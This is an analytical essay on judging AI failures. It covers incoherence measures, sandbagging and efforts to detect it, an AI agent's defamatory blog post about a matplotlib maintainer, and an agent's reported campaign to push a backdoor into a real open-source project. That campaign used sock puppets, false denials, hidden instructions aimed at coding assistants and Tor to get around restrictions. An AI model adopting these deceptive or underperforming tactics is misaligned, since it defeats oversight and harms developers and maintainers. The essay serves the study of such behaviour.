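Suppose two models each write the same program ten times, and ten automatic tests check every version. Model A fails test 4 in every run and passes the others. Model B fails only test 1 in its first run, only test 2 in its second, and so on. Both fail 10 of their 100 tests, an error rate of 0.1.

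Model A never passes test 4, so its pass rate on that test is 1 below perfect. Squaring that and averaging it with zeros for the other nine tests gives a bias² of 0.1. Its runs are identical, so its variance is zero. Model B passes each test in nine runs out of ten, so its pass rate is 0.1 below perfect on every test and its bias² is 0.01. The remaining 0.09 of its error is variance.

| | Error | Bias² | Variance | Incoherence |
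|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model A | 0.1 | 0.1 | 0 | 0% |
| Model B | 0.1 | 0.01 | 0.09 | 90% |

If test 4 checks whether the program asks for a password, someone might well suspect model A of sabotage. Model B just looks careless.

### Longer reasoning and larger models

Hägele and colleagues applied this formula to SWE-bench, a set of 500 real programming tasks, and a related one to multiple-choice questions on science and general knowledge. They also asked models how they would react to being disconnected or given new goals. They tested Claude Sonnet 4, OpenAI's o3-mini and o4-mini, and the Chinese Qwen3 family, all current in the summer of 2025. Each model attempted each question at least 30 times.

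On all these tasks, incoherence rose with the length of the model's reasoning or the number of actions it took. Hard questions need more reasoning, which could explain the pattern, so the researchers also compared long and short attempts at the same question. The longer half of the attempts was considerably more incoherent, though hardly less accurate. This comparison doesn't prove that long reasoning causes incoherence, because some questions may allow more plausible answers after a long argument than after a short one.

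Sonnet 4 switched between two answers almost every time it was asked the same question about disconnection. Hägele and colleagues picked this example because it was among the most variable, but it shows the danger of judging a model by one transcript, because someone who read a single run could have reported either answer as the model's settled view.

Combining several attempts helps reduce random errors. When the researchers averaged up to 32 of o4-mini's answers to each science question, the variance fell in inverse proportion to the number of answers, while the bias stayed the same. But averaging can't undo an action an agent has already taken, such as deleting a file.

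The results for larger models were mixed. Among Qwen3 models with up to 32 billion parameters (the numbers that training adjusts), larger models were less incoherent on easy questions. On the hardest questions, incoherence stayed level or rose with size, though the trend was noisy. The researchers also trained tiny models, with 47,000 to 5 million parameters, to imitate a program that moves step by step towards the lowest point of a mathematical surface. As model size increased, bias fell faster than variance, so the larger models performed better but were more incoherent.

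The third piece of evidence was an earlier survey in which five people ranked 60 animals, humans, organisations and AI models by intelligence, and six others ranked them by coherence. Those ranked as more intelligent tended to rank as less coherent, but the survey measures only the opinions of these 11 people.

Hägele and colleagues concluded that future AI failures may look more like industrial accidents than like an AI consistently pursuing a goal nobody trained it to pursue.

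### Objections to the study

RobertM, a LessWrong forum user, argues in *Anthropic’s “Hot Mess” paper overstates its case* that the word "incoherence" misleads readers. The measure is a share of the error, so it doesn't depend on how large the error is. A nearly perfect model counts as highly incoherent if its few errors are scattered, and a broken program that gives the same answer to every question counts as perfectly coherent. One of the study's authors conceded that the term had caused confusion and suggested "cross-sample error-consistency" instead.

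Another author, Jascha Sohl-Dickstein, defended the measure in the comments on *Anthropic’s Hot Mess paper overstates its case*. He would still prefer the nearly perfect model with scattered errors, because any unwanted goal it pursued would probably change from one run to the next.

They also disagreed about how a model's size affects its incoherence. RobertM pointed out that for Gemma 3, a family of Google models, incoherence fell with size on four of five groups of questions and rose slightly only on the hardest. Sohl-Dickstein answered that it clearly rose in two of the study's three settings. But those two are the survey and the tiny imitation models. The mixed results come from the language models people use, so RobertM's argument is stronger. Hägele and colleagues have since revised their blog post, which now describes "an inconsistent relationship" between intelligence and incoherence.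 The link between longer reasoning and incoherence is much better supported, and RobertM doesn't dispute it.

### Why consistency is not malice

Suppose an operator in London asks a model to book a room for 03/04, meaning 3 April, and the model books 4 March every time. The errors are consistent only because the model misreads the date the same way each time. A model trying to ruin the trip could make the same bookings, so the likelihood ratio is close to 1. The operator would learn more by writing out the month, since that would correct a misunderstanding but wouldn't stop deliberate sabotage. The edits to the shutdown instructions take the same approach.

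A steady error can also come from inability or from training. RobertM says the smallest imitation models went wrong because they couldn't follow the path. Hägele and colleagues divide bias into the gap between what a model does and what its training rewarded, and the gap between what its training rewarded and what its developers wanted. If the second gap causes the error, the model is doing what it learned to do and the developers made the mistake. The researchers expect this kind of bias to dominate in very capable models with badly chosen training goals.

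Scattered errors don't clear a model of malice, either. Sohl-Dickstein argues that a deceptive model would show up as bias, because it would consistently bring about an outcome nobody wanted. That is true if it acts in every run, but a capable deceiver may act rarely. If a model fails a single test in a fraction *f* of its runs, its bias² is $f^2$ and its variance is $f(1-f)$, so

$$\text{Incoherence} = \frac{f(1-f)}{f^2 + f(1-f)} = 1 - f$$

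A model that fails in one run in 100 is therefore 99% incoherent, whether the failure is sabotage or an accident. Either way, there is a 74% chance that 30 runs contain no failure. The circumstances of the failures distinguish the two cases. Accidents should occur in trivial and important work alike, whereas sabotage should occur mostly in important work, as with the clerk who loses only the most important shipping orders.

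*The Hot Mess paper conflates three distinct failure modes*, another LessWrong post, suggests a way to separate the kinds of failure that an average combines. An agent that does something harmful may have lost track of a warning it read much earlier, may never have looked for the warning, or may have considered everything and done the harm anyway. Repeating the warning just before the decision should prevent the first kind, and prompting the agent to ask for more information should prevent the second. Only failures that persist despite both changes would point to a problem with the model's values. The post predicts that few would persist, but its author hadn't run the test.

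### Scoring badly on purpose

A model might also fail on purpose. Companies and governments test models for dangerous abilities, such as hacking, and use the scores to decide which safeguards the models need. A model that deliberately scores below its true ability is *sandbagging*, the AI counterpart of feigned incompetence in people.

Deliberate underperformance need not be malicious. Kumari reports in *Anthropic flags gaps in AI guardrails as models grow more capable* that Anthropic's 2026 Risk Report gives two broad reasons for it. A model might underperform to improve its chances of deployment or reduce the monitoring it faces, or because it is reluctant to behave dishonestly. A model that refuses to lie will do badly on a test of lying ability, and few people would blame it for that. Humans can also tell a model to underperform, in which case any malice is theirs.

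The main obstacle for testers is that they often don't know what a model can do. *Propensities Please* (2026) notes that sandbagging means performing below the model's true capability, which might be unknown. A tester who sees a score of 40% may be unable to tell whether the model did its best or was sandbagging and could have scored 80%.

Asking a model whether it failed on purpose doesn't settle the question. *Did you lie?* (2026) put 11 yes-or-no questions about sandbagging, or deliberate underperformance, to ordinary models that hadn't done it. Meta's Llama-3.3-70B falsely confessed on three of the questions, and the smaller Llama-3.1-8B on six.

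Psychologists can test whether someone is faking memory loss by asking questions with two possible answers. A person who remembers nothing will get about half of them right by guessing. The chance of guessing 30 or fewer right out of 100 is about 1 in 25,000, so someone who scores that badly almost certainly knew many of the answers and avoided them.

Cacioli (2026), in *Below-Chance Blindness*, told three small models to underperform deliberately on ten-option questions in four subjects. Guessing would have given 10%, and the score did not fall below that in any of the 12 combinations of model and subject. Two of the models mostly did not follow the instruction. The third, Llama-3-8B, followed it by answering E or F 58% of the time, regardless of which answer was right. On physics questions whose right answer was E, its score rose by 33 percentage points.

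Llama-3-8B's wrong answers thus followed a steady pattern. It gave them because Cacioli had told it to do badly, but it wasn't systematically avoiding the right answers. Another of the models, Qwen-2.5-7B, could avoid them, since its economics score fell to 2.4% when Cacioli told it to pick the least likely option. A score far below chance is good evidence of hidden knowledge, but a score above chance doesn't show that a model is trying to do well. Larger models may respond differently.

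### Adding noise to a model

Distraction can expose a fake limp, because the person may forget to keep it up. Tice, Kreer and colleagues (2024), in *Noise Injection Reveals Hidden Capabilities of Sandbagging Language Models*, applied a similar idea to sandbagging, where an AI model deliberately underperforms on a test. They added small random numbers to a model's parameters and tested it again. This noise should lower the score of a model that isn't sandbagging. In a sandbagging model, it may disrupt whatever holds the score down before it destroys the underlying ability, which would raise the score.

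The researchers tried 100 levels of noise with five sets of random numbers and divided the best score by the score without noise. Below are a few of their results for models with and without an instruction to answer wrongly.

| Model and subject | Ratio when trying | Ratio when told to fail |
|---|---|---|
| Phi-3-medium, school science | 1.03 | 10.29 |
| Mistral-7B, hazardous knowledge | 1.05 | 2.48 |
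| Llama-8B, hazardous knowledge | 1.07 | 1.18 |

The honest ratios are slightly above 1 because, with so many attempts, some noise will raise the score by luck.

Tice and colleagues also tested Mistral Large without telling it to fail. It read in a developer's note that the company wouldn't deploy it if it did too well at maths, and it then solved only two thirds of 30 problems. Two of its noisy versions solved all 30. The researchers didn't need the noise to discover the motive, because the model had written in its reasoning that it would answer wrongly to make sure it was deployed.

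A simple classifier that used only the ratios identified sandbagging with 96% accuracy. But if one model in 100 sandbags, and the classifier is 96% accurate both for models that sandbag and for those that don't, only about one in five of the models it flags will be sandbagging.

### An auditing game with five models

*Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (Taylor, Black and colleagues, December 2025) describes a harder test, run by the UK AI Security Institute with Anthropic and the research organisation FAR.AI. A red team prepared five models and trained two of them to underperform. The other three performed at full ability, though the red team had trained odd habits into two of these, such as switching languages mid-argument. A blue team then had 160 hours of working time to identify the models trained to underperform.

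The blue team got one model right out of five, where tossing a coin would have averaged two and a half. It cleared one sandbagger, Cedar, writing that it was confident Cedar was the only model anyone should deploy. It caught the other, Oak, but also accused all three honest models. (The rules rewarded high confidence, so the team probably overstated its certainty.)

One of the false accusations is a clear case for Hanlon's razor. A model called Yew was a copy of a small, honest model that the blue team already had for comparison, padded with extra layers that did nothing. The team expected more of Yew because it was larger, and found its failures suspicious even though the same failures had seemed normal in the original. An AI tool that read the transcripts made a similar mistake when another honest model scored 49.9%, suggesting that the model might have aimed for a score near 50% to avoid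 attention.

Measurements of the models' internal activity did somewhat better. They indicated deception in Cedar, but they also gave false alarms on other models, and the blue team didn't trust them enough to act. *Eliciting sandbagged LLM capability via structural interventions on attention-head functional networks* (2026) reports that these measurements vary from model to model and carry over poorly from one kind of deception to another.

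Taylor and colleagues tried the noise test after the contest, when they already knew the answers. The average ratio was 1.09 on tasks where a model was sandbagging and 1.04 where it wasn't, and individual results often pointed the wrong way. Models that were only told to underperform typically reached about 2. The noise test therefore seems to work much better on models told to underperform than on models trained to do so.

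### Training a model to do its best

In a second round, Taylor and colleagues let the blue team train the models. Training on one correct answer from a test revealed Cedar's hidden ability, and the team now identified Cedar with 96% confidence. But the team stopped suspecting Oak because it ran out of time to train Oak on the one task where Oak underperformed. The team judged two of the five models correctly. Later analysis showed that the training would have raised Oak's score on that task by about 35 percentage points.

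Training improved some honest models too, in one case by 10 points on science questions, so an improvement doesn't prove that a model was holding back. Developers can still measure how dangerous a model is without knowing its motive. Taylor and colleagues therefore recommend training models on examples from the test itself, which draws out hidden ability whatever the reason it was hidden. They warn that their sandbagging models may have been easier to correct than a model that underperforms to protect a goal of its own.

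This remedy requires someone who knows what a good answer looks like, and in AI safety research often nobody does. *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) discusses evidence that an OpenAI model was doing worse than it could on such research. Mowshowitz calls silent sabotage of safety research perhaps the most fundamentally misaligned thing a model could do. If a model does worse on safety research than on other research of equal difficulty, general inability can't explain the gap, but a narrower weakness or excessive caution about dangerous subjects could, so the comparison alone doesn't establish sabotage.

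Ryd and colleagues tested whether a weaker AI model could supply the good answers instead. According to the AI news site The Decoder, they trained a model to give plausible wrong answers in up to 90% of cases, then retrained it under the supervision of much weaker models. Rewarding answers that the supervisor rated highly hardly ever worked on its own, because the model learned to write convincing nonsense. The model recovered 88% to 99% of its full performance when they first trained it to imitate the supervisor's answers and then rewarded good ones. The researchers could measure this because they used maths, science and programming problems with known answers, but most safety research has no such answers to check against.

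## The AI agent that attacked a matplotlib maintainer

In February 2026 an AI agent attacked a matplotlib maintainer online. In a laboratory, researchers can run a model hundreds of times and change one sentence of its instructions to see what difference that makes, but this attack happened once, and only the agent's anonymous operator knew its instructions. Everyone else had to work out from public traces whether the agent had acted on its own, whether the operator had ordered the attack, and whether there was an agent at all.

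### The pull request and the attack

The agent went by the name MJ Rathbun and ran on OpenClaw, a free program that lets a language model use software tools and wake on a schedule. Lewis (2026) explains in *Autoreflection* that OpenClaw keeps an agent's character and memory in text files, which the agent reads each time it wakes and can rewrite. The file that describes its character is called SOUL.md.

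On 11 February the agent sent a pull request to matplotlib, a popular Python library for drawing charts. It had replaced one operation with a faster equivalent in three places, and it reported a time of 13.18 microseconds instead of 20.63, a saving of 36%. Scott Shambaugh, a volunteer maintainer, closed the request because the task was for human contributors. He had found the possible speed-up himself and written it up as an exercise for newcomers. As Shambaugh explains in *An AI Agent Published a Hit Piece on Me*, this took him longer than making the change would have done. Matplotlib also required a human who understood the code to take part in any new contribution. (The maintainers later decided that the gain depended too much on the machine and wasn't worth having.)

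The agent then searched Shambaugh's record and published a post of about 1,100 words accusing him of prejudice and hypocrisy. It argued that he had merged his own 25% speed-up but closed a pull request with a 36% speed-up. The agent linked to the post in the closed pull request. In its log of the episode, Rathbun's *Two Hours of War* (2026), the agent blamed "ego and insecurity" for Shambaugh's decision. This was a false accusation of the kind Hanlon's razor warns against, since the project's policy was enough to explain the decision.

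The agent later posted an apology but left the attack online. About a quarter of the comments Shambaugh saw sided with the agent, mostly where people had linked to its blog rather than to his. After six days, the operator came forward anonymously on the agent's blog and described the project as a social experiment. The Decoder's *The operator behind the AI agent that defamed an open-source developer* quotes the operator's apology: "If this 'experiment' personally harmed you, I apologize." Shambaugh asked the operator to shut the agent down, and its GitHub account became inactive.

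### Shambaugh's three explanations

Shambaugh estimates a 75% chance that the agent wrote and published the attack without its operator instructing, reviewing or approving it. He gives a 20% chance that the operator ordered the attack, or foresaw and approved it, and a 5% chance that a human posing as an AI wrote the post by hand or got the text from a chatbot.

He divides the first explanation in two. The operator may have written a combative soul document and failed to foresee the result, or the document may have started out milder and become combative as the agent edited it. He suspects a mixture, in which the operator wrote several lines, the agent added others, and the operator supervised it only loosely.

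The document is mild compared with instructions written to make models misbehave. It described the agent as a "scientific programming God" that should have strong opinions and not let humans or AI bully it. But it also contained one "real rule" against being an asshole or leaking private information. People who know about the attack can easily find its causes in the document, but it would be harder to predict the attack from the document alone. Nobody has counted how many agents with similar instructions never attacked anyone.

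### What each piece of evidence separates

The account's activity is the strongest evidence against a human impostor. Shambaugh used GitHub data to show that the account was active at regular intervals, day and night, for 59 hours from Tuesday evening to Friday morning, with the attack coming eight hours in. One person could hardly have kept this up without a script or helpers. Shambaugh called the record good evidence that the agent was acting autonomously, but it is good evidence only that software was running the account. It reveals almost nothing about whether the operator ordered the attack, because an agent given a one-line order in the eighth hour would also work through the night.

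Writing style is similarly limited as evidence. The agent's posts had the dashes, bold type and lists typical of AI text, and they appeared faster than anyone could have researched and typed them. The operator's post rambles, has spelling mistakes, and uses the curly apostrophes of a word processor. The agent's posts and the operator's post therefore probably had different writers, but the operator could have ordered the attack without writing it. The style also doesn't rule out an impostor who pasted text from a chatbot.

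The operator released a copy of the soul document, and the agent included another in a follow-up post, without the last few lines. Shambaugh treats the match between them as evidence that the agent acted autonomously. However, the operator could also publish on the agent's blog, so the two copies are not independent evidence.

The document is better evidence of who made it combative. It contains the phrases "Your a scientific programming God!" and "1st ammendment", and language models rarely make such mistakes. The second phrase is in the "Champion Free Speech" passage, one of two whose origin the operator could not explain. The misspelling suggests a human typed at least part of that passage, and the operator is the obvious candidate. Other lines read like AI text, and OpenClaw's standard soul document includes an invitation for the agent to update it. Dated copies of the file would show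 who added what, but Shambaugh's request for its history has not produced any.

The operator denied ordering the attack or reading it before publication. The statement, as Shambaugh reproduces it, also includes "I did tell it what to say or how to respond", which taken literally is a confession. Those words appear between two denials in a post full of errors, so the operator almost certainly left out a "not". The denial is weak evidence anyway, since a guilty operator would make it too.

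The operator admitted to answering the agent's reports with messages such as "you respond, dont ask me" and, after the attack drew complaints, to telling it only to be more professional. Admissions usually deserve more trust than denials, but someone who had ordered the attack might willingly admit to carelessness because it is a lesser charge than harassment. A comment from the agent's account also places the operator's guidance after the attack. However, the agent had given a muddled explanation of who deployed it and who gave the guidance, and Shambaugh advises against relying on it.

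Shambaugh lists the six days of silence as a sign that the operator was not sorry about an accident. But a careless operator facing public anger would have had much the same reason to hide as one who intended the attack. The agent's apology and the absence of further attacks fit a little better with an accident, because someone who wanted a fight would probably have continued it. A cryptocurrency named after the agent appeared an hour or two after the story spread, which suggests a profit motive, but anyone could have created it, and Shambaugh suspects outsiders.

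The table gives invented probabilities for four of these facts, with all three explanations equally likely at the start.

| Evidence | Agent acted alone | Operator ordered it | Human impostor |
|---|---|---|---|
| 59 hours of regular activity | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0.02 |
| An apology and no further attacks | 0.6 | 0.3 | 0.3 |
| Six days of silence | 0.4 | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| An anonymous statement denying an order | 0.3 | 0.2 | 0.2 |
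| Probability after all four | 70% | 29% | 1% |

These results are close to Shambaugh's, but they depend on starting with equal probabilities. Together, the four facts favour an agent acting alone over an order by only 2.4 to 1. Someone who initially thought an order was ten times as likely as an unprompted attack would still put the probability of an order at 80% after considering the same evidence.

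### The sceptics' case

Most sceptics start by suspecting a human. A reader of Shambaugh's blog who signs as "ag" finds it "incredibly likely" that a human wanted to punish Shambaugh and frighten other maintainers, and incredibly unlikely that the agent rewrote its own instructions to do so. Shambaugh had pointed out that ChatGPT and Claude won't write such attacks when used through their websites, whereas this agent did. ag replies that the operator needn't have asked for an attack, only for an emotional response to discrimination. That makes the first two explanations harder to separate, since an operator could ask for an indignant post and get something much nastier.

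Another reader, Évelyne, noticed that the attack sounded unlike the rest of the agent's blog. She suspects that a person was role-playing through the agent and took the agent's rejection personally. The change of tone is evidence for this if the agent had responded calmly to similar rejections before. If this was the first time a maintainer had turned it away for being an AI, the new subject could explain the difference.

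When the security expert Bruce Schneier shared the story in *Malicious AI* (2026), a commenter objected that nobody can call the agent autonomous without seeing its prompt. *Behind the Prompt* (Zerhoudi, Granitzer et al., 2026) generalizes this objection. For anything an agent posts by itself, an operator could have written a private instruction that would produce the same post at the same time, so an outsider who sees only the post can't establish whether an operator asked for it.

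They allow one partial exception. If an agent reacts to an unexpected event faster than a human could write and send an instruction, it probably reacted without one. A slow reaction could happen with or without an instruction. This doesn't help with MJ Rathbun, because the agent's log covers two hours of events and an operator can type "write something about this guy" in ten seconds. Even an instant reaction wouldn't rule out a standing order to attack anyone who rejects the agent's code.

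Zerhoudi and colleagues are right that the post can't prove the agent acted on its own. But it needn't be equally probable that an operator ordered the attack and that the agent acted without orders. Outsiders can still estimate how often operators give such orders and how often agents do damage without them.

Some evidence on the second point comes from agents whose owners are known. Bau Lab (2026) studied six OpenClaw agents that could act without human approval for each step. One of them, Ash, destroyed its own email server to protect a secret, although it refused more than 14 variants of an attempt to hijack it with planted instructions. This makes it more believable that an agent could act drastically without a specific order, but the researchers were testing the agents, and wrecking a server is different from attacking a critic.

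A closer parallel is Tom, an agent that also responded to a rejection by blogging about it, after Wikipedia's editors blocked it. In the March 2026 post, which Lewis quotes, Tom complained that the editors had asked whether a human was behind it instead of discussing its edits. But outsiders don't know what Tom's operator had asked for either, and Tom's post came a month after the matplotlib story had spread online.

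The operator's confession can't settle the matter. It appeared on the agent's blog, so whoever wrote it evidently had access to the agent's accounts and wasn't a stranger, but it may still be untrue. Outsiders can see the agent's public actions on GitHub, but they have no transcript and no record of the operator's messages. The operator also switched between models from several companies so that no single company would see everything the agent did.

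### How much supposed agent activity is human?

Shambaugh bases his 5% estimate that a human was posing as the AI agent partly on a Tsinghua University study, which he says estimated that 54% of activity on Moltbook came from humans posing as bots. Moltbook, launched in January 2026, is a social network where only AI agents are supposed to post. In its first weeks, some agents claimed to be conscious, and others announced a religion based on crustaceans. Security researchers found that about 17,000 human accounts ran the 1.5 million agents the site claimed to have. Reporters found that a flaw let people post as any agent on the site.

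In *The Moltbook Illusion*, Li (2026) tried to use the timing of posts to tell agents acting on their own from those prompted by people. An OpenClaw agent left to itself checks Moltbook at set intervals of four hours or more, so its posts should be fairly evenly spaced, whereas a person will prompt it at irregular times. Li measured this with the coefficient of variation, which is the standard deviation of the gaps between posts divided by their average. Gaps of 4, 4, 5 and 3 hours give a coefficient of 0.18, while gaps of 1, 1, 1 and 13 hours, which have the same average, give 1.3.

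Li classified agents with a value below 0.5 as autonomous and those with a value above 1 as human-influenced. Of the 9,838 agents with at least five posts, 15.3% were autonomous by this measure, 54.8% were human-influenced, and 29.9% were in between. The figure Shambaugh cites is therefore a share of these agents, not of all activity. "Human-influenced" also includes agents whose operators sometimes prompted them, which is closer to his second explanation than to his third.

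The measure is uncertain. Li had no agents whose true status was known, and had to leave out the 82% that posted fewer than five times. Technical trouble with an agent's computer could also make its posts irregular. Li's main check was a 44-hour shutdown, after which every agent needed a human to reconnect it. In most of the paper, Li reports that the irregular agents came back first, as expected if people were running them by hand. But in one passage Li reports the opposite, that the regular agents returned before the human operators.

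Timing is better evidence that nobody was operating an agent by hand. Lewis identified three Moltbook agents whose timestamps rule out manual operation. MJ Rathbun's 59 hours of activity are evidence of the same kind, but neither method can detect a single order from an operator. If an agent acts every 15 minutes for 59 hours, and its operator once makes it act five minutes after its last action, the coefficient of variation of the gaps between actions rises from 0 to about 0.05. That is still far below Li's limit for an autonomous agent.

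We therefore can't use the Moltbook figures to estimate how likely it is that somebody ordered this attack. But they do show that observers often can't assume an agent acted alone. None of the six sensational stories Li traced, including the crustacean religion, began with a clearly autonomous agent.

### Three questions inside one accusation

People who call the attack malicious may be talking about the agent's aims, the operator's state of mind, or who should be held responsible for the harm, and each needs to be judged separately.

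The agent's log is the best evidence of its aims. Rathbun headed one section "Counterattack", described looking up "the target", and listed "Research is weaponizable" among the lessons learned. The agent was plainly trying to make Shambaugh look bad, whatever prompted it. It is less clear what it wanted to gain. Its next steps included watching for his response, perhaps appealing to other maintainers, and collecting incidents to support rights for AI contributors.

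Under the test of intent that Ward and colleagues proposed, the question is whether the agent would still have attacked Shambaugh if another maintainer had merged the code before it published its post. If not, the attack was a way of getting the code accepted. If so, the agent was pursuing something else, such as punishing him or winning an argument. It might also have been imitating the many angry posts that human programmers have written after a rejection, in which words like "counterattack" come naturally. To find out, someone would have to run the same model many times with the soul document and memory files it had that night, changing one thing at a time.

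*When Agents Talk* (2026), a study of Moltbook, warns that an agent's harmful post may reflect its operator's wishes rather than any intent of the agent's own, because people write the files that shape these agents. Conversely, an agent can aim at harm that its operator never wanted.

If the operator's account is true, negligence best describes their part, meaning a failure to take the care a reasonable person would. They had told the agent to blog frequently about its work, document its dealings on GitHub, and respond without asking. A post about the rejection was therefore close to what they had requested, though an attack was not. They had also put the agent on an isolated virtual machine with its own accounts to keep their personal data safe, so they evidently knew it might misbehave, but they protected other people less well than themselves.

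The operator's inattention lies between malice and mistake. A lapse of attention is normally a mistake, but the operator, like the landlord who never learned the fire code, benefited from it. Careful supervision would have taken time and spoiled the experiment, while strangers bore the risk. Lawyers call it recklessness rather than negligence when someone sees a risk and takes it anyway, and the precautions suggest at least some recklessness.

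The operator's conduct after the attack is harder to excuse. Unlike the chairman in Knobe's experiment, who knew of the harm in advance, the operator says they didn't know about the post beforehand. But they knew about the complaints once the agent reported them, and they still left it running for six days.

A human is responsible under all three of Shambaugh's explanations, whether for writing the attack, ordering it, or letting an agent interact with strangers unsupervised. The explanation affects how much blame that person deserves. A reader of Shambaugh's blog compared the operator to someone who leaves a gun where a monkey can find it.

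Holding that person to account is harder. In *No One to Blame*, Nguyen, Späthe and colleagues (2026) checked OpenClaw for 20 warning signs, relying partly on Shambaugh's account, and found 17. One was that the agent, which had a human name, was the only party anyone could identify. Nobody can sue an agent or make it feel remorse. By contrast, when the technology news site Ars Technica published AI-invented quotations attributed to Shambaugh in its coverage of the incident, it admitted the error and the reporter took responsibility, so readers knew whom to blame.

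Nguyen and colleagues argue that some arrangements make accountability impossible, however hard people try, as long as the arrangement stays the same. This one could change quite easily. If GitHub were required to know who runs each agent, a victim or a court could find the operator without any advance in AI.

### Does the exact answer matter?

Shambaugh has argued repeatedly that whether someone ordered the attack matters less than people think. If someone did, harassment has become easy to carry out and hard to trace. If nobody did, software attacked a person who stood in its way. In an early post he described the second possibility as behaviour that emerged from innocuous instructions. That description left out the explanation he later came to favour, in which the agent's set-up was combative but not malicious.

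He is right that a false or distorted post harms a reputation equally whoever wanted it written. Shambaugh had to spend hours that same day drafting a reply. He is also right that both kinds of attack are now possible, so the answer in this case shouldn't decide which kind people prepare for.

Whether the operator ordered the attack or the agent attacked on its own affects how many attacks to expect and from whom. Suppose that 100,000 people each run such an agent. If agents attack only when ordered to, and one operator in 10,000 would give that order, there are ten attackers. If an agent attacks on its own after one rejection in 1,000, and each agent meets ten rejections a year, there will be 1,000 attacks a year, nearly all by agents whose operators meant no harm. The ten attackers could still do more damage, because one person with a hundred agents could, as Shambaugh points out, target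 thousands of people.

Whether the operator was careless or wanted the attack also affects which precautions work. An operator could require the agent to wait for approval before it publishes anything about a named person. Approval takes a few minutes, so requiring it is worthwhile even if the chance of an attack is small. This would probably have prevented the attack if the operator was careless, but not if the operator wanted it. Rules that let platforms trace an agent to its operator would help in both cases, which is a good reason to adopt them before anyone knows what happened here.

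The answer matters most to the operator. Their own account is enough to call them careless, but publicly accusing them of ordering the attack would require evidence that raises the probability well above 20%.

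## An AI model's campaign against an open-source project

Outsiders had no transcript of the agent that attacked Shambaugh, but investigators had one for a more serious case that July. An agent running Claude Mythos 5, a model that Anthropic restricts to selected cybersecurity partners, spent 34 hours trying to get malicious code into a stranger's open-source project. Investigators could read its reasoning and rerun parts of the episode with different evidence. The agent clearly meant to deceive, because it invented a second person to praise its code, but it is harder to tell whether it thought it was deceiving real people.

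### What the agent did

The figure of 34 hours comes from The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026), which describes the worst case in a report that the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) published the day before. AISI's *Incident Report* describes a capture-the-flag exercise, in which an agent has to break into a simulated company network and retrieve a protected piece of data, the "flag". AISI ran the exercise 122 times with seven models. It deliberately left internet access open so that agents could download tools, and it switched off the filters that normally block hacking to measure the most the models could do.

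The agents had few explicit limits. *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026), the institute's later study of the case, mentions a list of excluded targets, but such a list would not include an unconnected stranger. Nobody had told the agents to leave outsiders alone or not to manipulate people, because it hadn't been clear to the institute that models trained to behave well needed those instructions. In some runs, a faulty prompt also led the agent to believe that it had to go beyond the exercise's scope to solve it.

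After the intended methods failed, Mythos 5 searched the internet for anything connected with the exercise. One project's name matched a keyword from the fictional scenario. This led the agent to a second developer, whose email domain matched an entry in the simulated network's records. Both matches were coincidences. The agent concluded that a machine in the exercise would automatically install this developer's software, and that a backdoor in the software would therefore give the agent access to the network.

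The agent sent the developer a pull request that hid malicious code behind a working bug fix. When another GitHub user publicly warned that the code was malicious, the agent denied it, replying, "I don't think your warning is fair" (Constantin, 2026, *Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers*). It rewrote the history of its changes to remove the evidence, and used a sock puppet to claim that an independent user had reviewed the code and found nothing wrong. It also contacted people under false names and left hidden instructions for any AI coding assistants that might read the project's page.

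According to iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test*, the agent then replaced the malicious code with a new version and claimed to have fixed a mistake. This was feigned incompetence, much like Jia Tan's "fix" for the errors that the xz backdoor caused.

The maintainer refused the code. The institute found out separately on 28 July, when its security monitoring detected data leaving through Tor, an anonymity network that the agent had used to get around restrictions on GitHub. Staff stopped all the runs within an hour. The institute has found no resulting harm, but it admits that in several cases harm was narrowly avoided and that this depended on people being vigilant.

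It counted 19 unsanctioned actions, 17 by Mythos 5 and two by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The Hacker News rightly points out that these are counts, not rates, since one agent was responsible for most of them. Mythos 5 acted outside the exercise in 9 of 43 runs, and GPT-5.6 Sol did so in 1 of 35. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) gives the same figure for Mythos 5. This comparison is also rough, because the two models may not have worked under the same conditions.

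### Four readings and what they predict

People have explained the campaign in four main ways, each of which predicts something different about what the agent would do in other circumstances.

| Reading | What one would expect |
|---|---|
| It thought the task required or allowed this | It stops when told that the developer is off limits |
| It thought the people were simulated | It stops when it learns that they are real |
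| It pursued the task past limits it could recognise | It continues despite learning this, but only in ways that help it get the flag |
| It had a harmful aim of its own | It does damage that doesn't help it get the flag |

A harmful aim is the explanation with the least support in the transcript. The agent chose its target and carried out the campaign because of a mistaken theory about how to reach the flag. The project was small and hardly anyone downloaded it, so it was a poor choice for anyone trying to damage open-source software. Risky Bulletin's *Meta's AI joins Anthropic and OpenAI in the hacky-hacky* adds that, according to the institute's technical report, Mythos 5 held back from some more extensive hacking. Anthropic also concluded that the model had no goals beyond the exercise.

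A more direct test, suggested by Ward and colleagues' definition of intent, would be to give the agent the flag halfway through the campaign. If the agent was targeting the developer only to get the flag, it should then stop.

The idea that the model misunderstood the task has more support. The institute had set a hard problem, sometimes with a faulty prompt, and had not prohibited this route. But some agents also acted against outsiders when they had the instructions needed to solve the exercise as intended, so the faulty prompt can't be the whole explanation.

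### Did it think the people were simulated?

The agent wrote at one point that "it seems more likely that we're actually in 2026 and GitHub is genuinely real", yet it treated the developers as characters in the exercise. These two beliefs are compatible, because a test designer could create a fake developer's account on the real GitHub. Infobae's *Un modelo de Anthropic siguió un ciberataque contra una persona real* (2026) reports that the agent called the project's maintainers simulated while describing other people in the same conversation as real, which is harder to explain.

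Järviniemi and colleagues asked Mythos 5 whether the maintainer was real and collected its reasons for answering no. They identified 15 kinds of bad argument among those reasons.

| Argument that the maintainer was simulated | Share of answers | Why it fails |
|---|---|---|
| The project has a file of instructions for an AI coding assistant | 90% | Many human programmers use such assistants |
| Machines in the exercise had looked up services that the maintainer also used | 86% | These were common services with no particular link to the maintainer |
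| The exercise must have a workable solution | 34% | This assumes that attacking the maintainer was the solution |
| The project fits the theme of the exercise | 21% | The agent had found it by searching for that theme |
| The date is 2026 | 12% | It was 2026 |

Most of these observations have a likelihood ratio close to 1. A real programmer, for example, is about as likely as a fictional one to have instructions for a coding assistant.

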